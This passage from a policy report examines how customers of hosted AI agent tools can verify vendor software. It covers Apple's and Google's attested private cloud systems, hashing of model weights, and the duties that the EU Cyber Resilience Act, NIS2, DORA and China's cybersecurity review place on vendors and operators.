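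Apple could sign a special version of its software to use on one person, but her phone would reject it unless Apple had listed it in a public log where researchers could see it. Apple would also have trouble steering her request to a particular server, because requests reach the load balancer without information identifying the sender.

Apple promises to publish each version of the software within 90 days of listing it in the log, or once relevant updates are available if that is sooner. Phones may therefore send data for up to three months to software that no outsider has examined. The log makes it likely that a harmful version will eventually be discovered, which may deter a company with a reputation to lose, but it doesn't protect the first users.

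### What outsiders have found in Apple's system

Anyone with a recent Mac and 16 gigabytes of memory can examine the software that runs on Apple's Private Cloud Compute servers. Apple's *Security research on Private Cloud Compute*, from October 2024, introduced a research environment that runs a slightly modified version of this software on the Mac. Researchers can download each release, check the log for consistency, and modify the software to see how it behaves. Apple also published the source code of some components, including the one that checks attestations, and offered up to $1 million for the most serious flaws.

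This openness has already exposed a flaw. Sentry's *Beyond Prompt Injection* (2026) describes how Drinor, a researcher who works with the security company, used the research environment to find a mistake in the program that sets up a server as it starts. An attacker could use the mistake to write files with full administrator rights and redirect operating data to their own server. Drinor received $150,000, the same amount as the maximum in Apple's 2024 reward list for reaching user data from a privileged network position. The attack required supplying the server's configuration, so an insider could have attempted it more easily than an ordinary user.

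Attestation could not have revealed this flaw, because the faulty program was Apple's genuine one. In the published source code, a function meant to validate part of the configuration was empty. The flaw also shows why a customer needs to know whether m covers a server's settings as well as its programs. Outsiders could see the empty function only because Apple had released the code, and no one reported the flaw until 2026.

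Apple also commissions quarterly audits of how it prepares and protects the servers, and the most recent covers the year to April 2026. The auditors give no opinion on the AI services, so the audits don't show that the summaries are accurate or that the models are safe.

Trail of Bits, a security consultancy, welcomed the design in *PCC* (2024) but pointed out that Apple effectively owns the attestation keys. Apple also designs the server chip, writes the software and supplies the phone that checks both. An outside thief or a rogue administrator would find it hard to get past all three, but the arrangement offers much less to a customer who distrusts Apple as a whole.

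In June 2026 Apple extended the service to Google's data centres, where the servers use Intel processors, NVIDIA's AI chips and a Google security chip. According to Apple's *Expanding Private Cloud Compute*, the attestation of any component that could leak user data relies on at least two independent manufacturers. Apple also keeps a permanent register of the machines. *Powering the next era of Confidential AI* (Patil and Lagar-Cavilla, 2026) adds that Apple and Google developed open-source software for the host machines so that outsiders can inspect it. Apple planned to phase in the full set of protections over the summer, so the early months in Google's data centres were not a fair test of the finished design.

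### Google's Private AI Compute

Google introduced a similar service, Private AI Compute, in November 2025 and published a review of it by the security company NCC Group, whose ten consultants had spent 100 working days on the system. *Private AI Compute in the Cloud* (Anderson, Bakos Lang et al., 2025) describes an important difference from Apple's design. The user's phone relied on Google to check the server's software, while an iPhone does the check itself. The phone trusted a fixed public key. Google's internal key store held the matching private key and used it only for servers that had a token from Borg Prime, the system that coordinates work across Google's network. Borg Prime checked a server's attestation before issuing the token.

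| | Apple's Private Cloud Compute | Google's Private AI Compute, November 2025 |
|---|---|---|
| Who compares the server's software with the approved versions | The user's device | Google's internal systems |
| What the public can inspect | The program files of every release and some source code | The hashes of the program files |
| Outside examination | Research environment, rewards, audits of server preparation | A review that Google commissioned |

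A published hash without the file lets an outsider notice that Google has changed something, but not what the change does.

The consultants concluded that Google had strongly limited the risk of exposing user data, "unless Google, as a whole organization, decides to do so". For instance, Google could make Borg Prime issue a false token to a server that copies the data elsewhere. The specific faults they reported were less serious. Under particular conditions, someone might identify a user from the timing of traffic, and attackers could overload parts of the system. Google said that it was fixing the overload problem and that the large number of users made the timing attack difficult.

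The consultants acknowledge gaps in their review. It excluded AMD's protected-computing platform, on which part of the system runs, and the phone apps. Google crashed the programs to show that a crash would not save user data, while the consultants watched over a shared screen. They could not confirm Google's statement that only three programs handle raw user data. Google commissioned the work, but their blunt statement about Google's ultimate power suggests they were not simply writing what their client wanted to hear.

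Google has since moved closer to Apple's approach. Pogorelec (2026), in *Google plans to give Private AI Compute a memory that follows users*, reports that in September Google published a tamper-proof record of its server software and the results of an independent audit. Phones will be able to check that the software is authentic before they send personal data. Google also plans to store users' context, in encrypted form with the keys on their devices, whereas its servers previously kept nothing after each task. This makes the system harder to protect, because a flaw in a server could expose older information whenever the server decrypts it, as well as the requests it is handling at the time.

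### Confirming that the served weights are the tested ones

A bank that tests a model for months wants to know that its staff are using the same model afterwards. The first step is model signing, in which the developer hashes every file of weights, lists the hashes in a manifest and signs the manifest. Anyone who downloads the weights can then detect a swapped or damaged file.

If the model runs on a remote server, the bank also needs attestation. The server's software would hash the weights as it loads them and include the hash in the attestation report. The bank would record the hash during its tests, and before each session its own program would compare the reported hash with the recorded one and stop if they differed. This works even if the developer keeps the weights secret, because a 256-bit hash reveals practically nothing about a file of several hundred gigabytes. The software that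 computes the hash has to be part of m, because otherwise a dishonest operator could make the server report the expected hash whatever weights it had loaded.

The hash of the weights does not cover everything that shapes an answer. A vendor could add a new system prompt, an output filter or an adapter without changing the original file's hash, so the attestation report should cover these too. With such a report, a customer could have noticed when Anthropic imposed hidden limits on Fable 5, provided that the report covered the component containing them.

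The hash comparison also can't show whether a change was trivial. If the vendor converts the weights to a more compact number format to save memory, the hash changes completely, even if the answers hardly change. The bank then has to decide whether to repeat its tests.

### What business customers can buy

No large vendor of agent tools appears to give business customers an attested hash of the model weights that produced each answer. Anthropic publishes signed checksums for Claude Code, but they cover only the client.

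Apple's system may be the closest. Its servers protect model files from alteration in the same way as programs, and they now run agents as well as single requests. The table of contents of Apple's security guide, as recorded by the tracking service ConductAtlas, includes an agent that coordinates tool calls and another that keeps limited information between requests. But Apple built the system for features on its own devices, while the water company needs an agent that can write to its ticket system. Apple's 2024 research environment also came with demonstration models, so outsiders who use it to examine the software are not testing the models that users get.

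Google Cloud offers software that lets a customer's program verify a protected server before sending prompts to it. A bank could combine this with an open-weight model and its own agent, include the hash of the weights in the check, and control the whole system. This approach requires engineers most waterworks do not have, and it rules out the closed models that many agent products depend on.

### Genuine software on chips that someone has to trust

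Even a perfect attestation would not reveal an undetectable backdoor in a model, because it would confirm only that the server was running the same model the bank had tested. It would not prevent prompt injection either, which works just as well on a server running exactly the software the vendor promised. Attestation of the model's server also does not protect data once the agent sends it to an add-on or a contractor's portal.

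The customer also has to trust whoever makes the chips. Anderson and colleagues explain that any practical AI service must process unencrypted data, so the hardware's designer could always build in a way to extract that data. Methods for computing on encrypted data can handle only simple tasks, such as producing a digital signature, and running a modern AI model takes millions to billions of times more computation. Even Google depends on another chipmaker. TechRadar's *Google turned to AMD Epyc, not its own Axion chips* reports that Google's first AI chip for confidential computing, announced in November 2026, works alongside AMD processors.

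Attackers can sometimes get around the protection without breaking the encryption. *SNPeek*, a research tool presented at the NDSS security conference, collects traces of memory and cache use from the machine that hosts an AMD protected environment. An attacker can use these traces to infer what the program inside is processing. Such an attack requires control of the host machine, so it matters most to customers who fear the cloud company itself or an intruder in its data centre. Apple acknowledges the danger and says it does not rely on protected computing alone. It uses two independent manufacturers, so a key stolen from one should not be enough to fake a server's identity.

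### Why vendors keep their software secret

Vendors' most obvious reason for withholding their software is commercial. Competitors could learn from published software, and a developer cannot recall leaked weights. This is a good reason to withhold files from the public, but it doesn't justify withholding all evidence about them. Apple publishes program files without most of the source code, and a hash reveals even less.

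The second reason is abuse detection, since abusers can adapt if a vendor explains exactly how it detects attempts to copy its model or use stolen accounts. But some checks can run inside the protected system. In Google's design, separate protected servers filter each answer for violations of company policy before it reaches the user, so no employee has to read it.

Detecting a pattern across many accounts is more difficult. A vendor that deletes every request and does not know who sent it can hardly discover that thousands of accounts are working together. Google's anonymous tokens limit how often a device can use the service, but they don't show what the requests have in common. A bank that asks its vendor for complete privacy is therefore also asking the vendor to give up a means of catching criminals. To compensate, the bank could keep its own logs and agree to search them when the vendor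 reports a suspicion.

Inspection by a trusted third party is a compromise between publishing the code and keeping it entirely secret. An inspector reads the software under a confidentiality agreement and publishes the hash of the version examined, along with a description of what it collects and when its behaviour changes. Customers can then use attestation to check that this version is running, while the code stays hidden from them and from the vendor's competitors. A similar arrangement can keep tests confidential too. *Google DeepMind Seals Gemini Test to Protect Benchmarks* (Abdullahi, 2026) describes a trial with Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite, an older small model, that used cryptography to keep both the test questions and the weights confidential. An inspector for the banking sector could use such a method to test a closed model on realistic fraud cases without revealing them to its developer.

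The main difficulty is keeping up with updates. A statement about one version does not apply to the next, and a thorough first review of a system like Google's takes 100 working days. If reviewing the changes took ten working days per release, a vendor with weekly releases would need 520 days of review a year. That is two to three full-time inspectors, which a large AI company can afford but the maker of a small add-on cannot. Urgent security fixes would have to go out before the inspector had finished, with a clear label and a deadline for the review.

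Customers also have to trust the inspector, who usually depends on the vendor for payment and access. Banks or water utilities could reduce this dependence by jointly hiring an inspector and agreeing on the questions in advance. For an agent tool, the inspector should report every setting that changes what the client sends, every condition under which the server treats customers differently, and every way to change those settings or conditions without a new release.

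## What European and Chinese law lets operators demand

A vendor can refuse to let an inspector examine its software unless a law or contract obliges it to cooperate. The EU has three relevant laws. The Cyber Resilience Act applies to companies that make software and connected devices, the NIS2 directive to essential services such as waterworks and hospitals, and the Digital Operational Resilience Act (DORA) to banks and other financial firms. China relies mainly on a security review of what critical infrastructure operators buy. Legislators drafted the European laws before agent tools became common, so applying them to such tools involves some guesswork.

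### What the Cyber Resilience Act requires of manufacturers

The European Union's *Cyber Resilience Act* (2024) has required manufacturers to report certain attacks since 11 September 2026, and most of its other duties begin on 11 December 2027. From then on, a manufacturer must limit the data its product processes, exercise due diligence over third-party components, and handle vulnerabilities for at least five years, or for the product's expected life if that is shorter. Security updates must install automatically by default, but customers must be able to turn this off. Where technically feasible, manufacturers must also deliver security updates separately from new functions, so a utility that pins its software could take a fix without accepting the rest of the release.

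Most manufacturers will check their own compliance, because agent tools are not on the act's list of products that need stricter assessment. Browsers are on that list, so a browser with a built-in agent may need an outside assessor unless its maker follows a technical standard that the EU has recognised. No such standard existed in late July, according to an independent guide, cyberresilienceact.eu's *On 27 July 2026, the Commission Published Its First Official Guidance* (2026).

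The reporting duty covers severe incidents, such as one that could lead to malicious code running on a customer's network, and vulnerabilities that attackers are already exploiting. The manufacturer must send an early warning within 24 hours of becoming aware and a fuller notification within 72 hours. The final report is due within 14 days of a fix for a vulnerability, or within a month of the fuller notification for an incident. The reports go to a national response team and normally also to ENISA, the EU's cybersecurity agency. The manufacturer must also tell affected users, but the act sets no deadline in hours for that.

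The 24-hour reporting period starts later than a customer might expect. *The new CRA guidance in practice* (2026), by the security consultancy SCHUTZWERK, explains that a manufacturer becomes "aware" only once an initial assessment makes the exploitation or incident reasonably certain. ENISA's reporting platform does not yet record that moment, so an authority must rely on the manufacturer's own records to judge whether a report was late.

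LiteLLM's malicious release of 21 October came less than six weeks after the reporting duty began, and code that steals credentials plainly counts as a severe incident. BerriAI offers LiteLLM in free and paid editions. If the malicious code reached paying customers in the EU, the company had to report it. For the free edition, the European Commission's guidance gives such a company only the lighter duties of an open-source steward, an organisation that supports free software intended for commercial use. Stewards need not report until 11 December 2027, according to *ENISA launched the CRA Single Reporting Platform for actively exploited vulnerabilities* (Markovic, 2026).

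The marker in Claude Code would probably not have been reportable, because no attacker exploited it and Anthropic had added it on purpose. The rule on limiting data might apply to a similar function after December 2027, though a vendor could argue that its product needs the data to prevent abuse.

### Client, hosted model and free add-on

Whether the Cyber Resilience Act covers an agent tool depends on where each part runs and who made it. The European Commission's guidance of 27 July uses 67 examples to address many such questions, according to *Commission publishes new guidance to support timely Cyber Resilience Act implementation*. The guidance is not binding, but national authorities will probably follow it.

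The client is the easiest part to classify. According to Orrick's *EU Cyber Resilience Act* (2026), a law firm's summary of the guidance, the act covers software that customers download or install and operate on their side. Claude Code fits this description. An agent that a planner opens in her browser is normally a remote service outside the act, even if it does the same work.

A hosted model counts as part of the product if it processes data remotely, the product could not perform one of its functions without it, and the manufacturer developed the software or took responsibility for its development. Anthropic's servers probably meet all three conditions for Claude Code. But most agent products run on another company's model. SCHUTZWERK treats a third party's generic storage service as a dependency that the manufacturer must assess in proportion to the risk. A third party's model would presumably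 be treated the same way, so the maker of the client would have to carry out due diligence on a model it cannot inspect.

The act defines software as "computer code". A lawyer could argue that this excludes model weights, which are numbers, and skills that consist entirely of English instructions, although the program that loads them is clearly software. Orrick reports that the Commission may address the act's overlap with the EU's AI Act and with DORA in later guidance.

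Free add-ons are the largest gap. The act does not cover a hobbyist who publishes an open-source skill and earns nothing from it. If an agent's maker builds that skill into its product, the maker must exercise due diligence over it, but a skill the customer adds later is not part of what the maker sold. A publisher who makes money indirectly can lose the exemption. The publisher of money-radar, the skill that steered OpenClaw users to financial products with referral codes, might count as a manufacturer, though an authority would still have to find the publisher.

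### NIS2 and the duties of essential services

NIS2 covers mostly medium-sized and large organisations in sectors such as energy, drinking water, health care and public administration. It is a directive and takes effect through national laws, so a waterworks has to consult its own country's statute. Member states had to adopt these laws by October 2024, but many were late.

Article 21 of the directive requires operators to manage the security of their supply chains. They must consider the vulnerabilities of each direct supplier, the quality of its products and its development practices. For the water company, the supplier of the agent's client is a direct supplier, and so is the model's developer if the company has a contract with it. If the client's maker buys access to the model, the developer is an indirect supplier. The same article requires security in acquiring and maintaining systems,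 so the company cannot ignore a free skill, even though the stranger who published it is hardly a supplier in the ordinary sense.

These duties fall on the operator. NIS2 does not oblige a vendor to answer the water company's questionnaire or admit its inspectors, so the company needs a contract that does. Under recital 13 of the Cyber Resilience Act, any buyer can set stricter requirements than the act's own, and member states can impose additional ones on products that essential services use. A recital explains a law and does not create a right, but this one makes it hard for a vendor to claim that customers can ask for no more than the act's minimum.

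NIS2 also applies directly to cloud providers of at least medium size, probably including some companies that host models. The Cybersecurity Coalition, an industry group, complains that the July guidance leaves such companies exposed to duplicate obligations when their cloud service is also part of a product. The overlap costs vendors money, but the free add-ons that neither law clearly covers are a bigger worry for customers.

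### DORA and the right to inspect

The law lets banks demand more. DORA has applied since 17 January 2025, and Articles 28 and 30 specify what a financial firm's contracts with technology suppliers must contain. All such contracts must describe the service, state where the supplier processes data, and oblige the supplier to help after an incident, either free or at a price agreed in advance. If the service supports a critical or important function, the contract must also give the bank and its supervisor rights of access, inspection and audit. The bank also needs an exit plan for events such as Anthropic's withdrawal of Fable 5 in June.

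A hosted agent that screens payments for fraud would very likely fall under the stricter rules, whereas one that formats slides would not. Whether DORA covers the client software is less certain, because it applies to digital services supplied on an ongoing basis, and a one-off software licence may not qualify. A client that updates itself every week looks much more like a service. If the bank buys access to a model through a cloud company, the developer may be only a subcontractor, and the bank has to make sure that its rights extend to the developer.

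DORA's contract rules are also hard to apply to free add-ons, because nobody has signed a contract with the bank. The bank still has general duties to manage and test its own systems, so it should treat the add-on as its own code. DORA's list of possible tests includes source-code reviews "where feasible", which is realistic for a short skill.

A bank's auditors could exercise their right to inspect Anthropic's premises and examine its logs and access controls without learning whether the model has a hidden trigger. If an inspection would affect the supplier's other customers, DORA allows other forms of assurance, which might include reports from an inspector that several banks share.

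European supervisors can examine the largest suppliers directly. Their first list of critical suppliers, from November 2025, had 19 companies, including the cloud businesses of Amazon, Google and Microsoft, but not Anthropic or OpenAI.

### China's review of purchases

China's Cybersecurity Law requires operators of critical information infrastructure to submit a purchase for review if it may affect national security. Under the Cybersecurity Review Measures, in force in their current form since February 2022, the operator itself first judges whether a purchase meets that condition. Officials then consider whether someone could use the product to control or disrupt the infrastructure, how open and reliable its supply is, and whether politics, diplomacy or trade could interrupt that supply. A review ordinarily takes a few months, but considerably longer if the case is difficult.

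The operator must also get the supplier to promise to cooperate with the review and not to obtain users' data illegally, take control of their equipment, or cut off supply or necessary support without good reason. The last promise addresses much the same danger as the one posed by the June export order, though a promise made under Chinese law would not have allowed an American company to disobey the order.

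The measures name cloud services and large application software among the products that may need review, so a hosted model or an agent used across a whole bank could qualify. It is less clear whether a free add-on, such as a skill, qualifies, because nobody buys it. The fine for using a product without a required review is one to ten times the purchase price, so the fine for a free skill would be zero. The managers responsible can still face personal fines, and the authorities can order the operator to stop using the product.

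Separate rules in the same law apply to products generally. They require suppliers to tell users and get their consent if a product collects their information, and to fix and report security flaws. These are the legal requirements closest to the National Vulnerability Database's complaint about Claude Code.

An amended version of the law took effect on 1 January 2026. It raised fines and added an article on AI, which commits the state to support research, develop ethical rules and strengthen risk monitoring. The article does not specify anything a bank could demand from an agent's supplier.

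The more detailed texts on agents are advisory. Freshfields reports that China's national cybersecurity standards committee issued draft guidelines in March for tools like OpenClaw. They recommend lists of approved add-ons, encrypted credentials, limits on resource use and manual approval of high-risk actions. A Chinese bank could write these measures into a contract, but the draft itself does not bind the vendor. Freshfields calls a similar statement by Hong Kong's privacy commissioner, together with non-binding guidance elsewhere, "an initial sticking plaster response".

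On 18 June China's state security authorities also warned of several recent attacks through open-source repositories and commercial tools, according to GMT8 Press' *Software "Supply Chain Poisoning" is gaining momentum* (2026). Such a warning can influence what a state-owned company buys, but it gives operators no right to inspect anything.

### What a bill of materials shows

Both European and American authorities want suppliers to document their components. The US National Security Agency's guidance of March 2026 treats training data, models, software, hardware, infrastructure and outside services as one AI supply chain. It recommends bills of materials for both software and AI, integrity checks, registries of trusted models and regular security tests, according to *NSA issues guidance on AI supply chain risks and cybersecurity vulnerabilities*, a summary by the digital-policy project CADE.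 The guidance is only advice, and it also warns of hidden backdoors in models, which a component list cannot detect.

The US government's minimum contents for an ordinary software list, from 2021, are the supplier, the component's name and version, other identifiers, its dependencies, the list's author and the time of writing. CISA proposed in 2025 to add a hash, the licence, the tool that generated the list and the stage at which it did so. The G7's cybersecurity working group has also worked on a version for AI that covers models and data sets. For the water company's agent, a fictional entry might look like this:

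| Field | Entry |
|---|---|
| Component and version | Field Agent client 4.2.1 |
| Supplier | Example Agents GmbH |
| File hash | SHA-256, beginning 9f2c |
| Licence | Proprietary |
| Direct dependency | Sensor-store MCP server 2.0.3 |
| Second-level dependency | LiteLLM 1.82.6, which the MCP server needs |
| Model | Example-LM 5, hosted by its developer; weights not hashed |
| Training data | Developer's summary, May 2026 |
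| System prompt | Hash of the client's part; server's part not listed |
| Author and time | Supplier's build system, 3 November 2026, 09:14 UTC |

An entry for LiteLLM 1.82.6 in the supplier's list of software components would be useful, because that version has the flaw in the gateway's key check that the company disclosed after the March attack, and anyone searching the list for it would find it at once. However, the Cyber Resilience Act requires the list to cover only top-level dependencies, so the supplier could lawfully leave that entry out. The customer may not see the list anyway. A manufacturer must draw one up and give it to an authority that has good reason to request it, but can decide whether to share it with users.

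Even a complete list of components would not reveal hidden behaviour. Anthropic added the marker to Claude Code by changing its own code, which does not require a new component. The lists for versions 2.1.90 and 2.1.91 could have been identical except for the version number and the hash. Model weights with a hidden trigger would also appear as an ordinary entry with a matching hash.

The entry also does not show the agent's current permissions or whether a stolen token still works. If the water company closed its account on the contractor's portal, the agent could reach fewer systems, but the entry would stay the same. The vendor cannot supply this information because it depends on the water company's accounts, so the company needs its own register of the agent's accounts, tokens and further connections. It has to update the register whenever an administrator changes an access right, even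 if the software stays the same.

### Before purchase, after an incident and after a refusal

| Rules | Before purchase | After an incident | If the vendor refuses inspection |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cyber Resilience Act (most duties from December 2027) | The manufacturer provides instructions and a declaration of conformity | The manufacturer reports to authorities and informs affected users | The customer has no right to inspect, but an authority can demand documents |
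| NIS2 | The operator assesses its suppliers | The operator reports significant incidents, with a first warning within 24 hours | The operator must reduce the risk or choose another supplier |
| DORA | The bank obtains the required contract terms | The bank reports major incidents, and the supplier must help | The bank should not use the supplier for a critical function; supervisors can inspect suppliers on their critical list |
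| Chinese rules | The operator applies for review where national security may be at risk | The supplier fixes and reports flaws; operators of critical infrastructure report serious incidents within an hour | The purchase can fail its review |

Only DORA requires contracts that let the customer inspect the vendor, and only for important functions. Even then, a bank cannot force a vendor to sign. A large bank may persuade the vendor because it can take its business elsewhere. A small waterworks usually has to accept standard terms, but it could negotiate better ones by buying jointly with other utilities, or ask its national authority to request the documents it cannot obtain itself.

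The American supply-chain-risk statutes at issue in Anthropic's dispute with the Pentagon work more like the Chinese review. They let the state exclude a supplier but do not help a customer inspect the product's internals.

### Paperwork, volunteers and trade policy

The Cyber Resilience Act requires regular security tests, and manufacturers must include the test reports in the technical file. According to Orrick, the guidance does not let a manufacturer simply repeat the same test at intervals; it must check whether new threats call for different ones. These requirements only partly answer the criticism that the European rules produce documents rather than evidence. A manufacturer can still assess its own agent tool, declare that it complies and keep the component list to itself, and an operator can satisfy an auditor with completed questionnaires. Customers have no general right to see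 the test reports, and none of the act's requirements specifically calls for a search for hidden triggers or for tests of several add-ons together.

The final text of the act largely spares volunteers from liability for software they give away. Open-source developers had feared it would not. People who only contribute code are not responsible for the product, a donation link does not make a project commercial, and stewards face no fines. Companies that find a flaw in a free component must report it to the maintainers and share any fix they write, which could reduce the volunteers' work. The Cybersecurity Coalition still objects that an organisation offering only incidental support cannot be sure whether it counts as a steward. Operators remain responsible for checking add-ons, even when the authors have no obligations to them.

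Security reviews can also serve trade policy. In May 2023 China's internet regulator announced that products from Micron, an American memory-chip maker, had failed a security review, and told operators of critical infrastructure to stop buying them. It published no technical details, so outsiders could not tell whether the chips had a flaw or China was retaliating for the limits Washington had placed on chip exports to China several months earlier.

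The defence of such bans is that a supplier's nationality can be a real security risk. A review of code alone, for example, would have missed the danger of the June export order. The EU accepts this argument too, since the Cyber Resilience Act lets member states restrict suppliers because of "non-technical factors". Such decisions are easier to trust when the authority separates technical findings from political judgement, publishes as much evidence as it safely can, and lets the supplier respond. If it does none of this, a utility in another country learns little about the product from the ban and still has to run its own tests.
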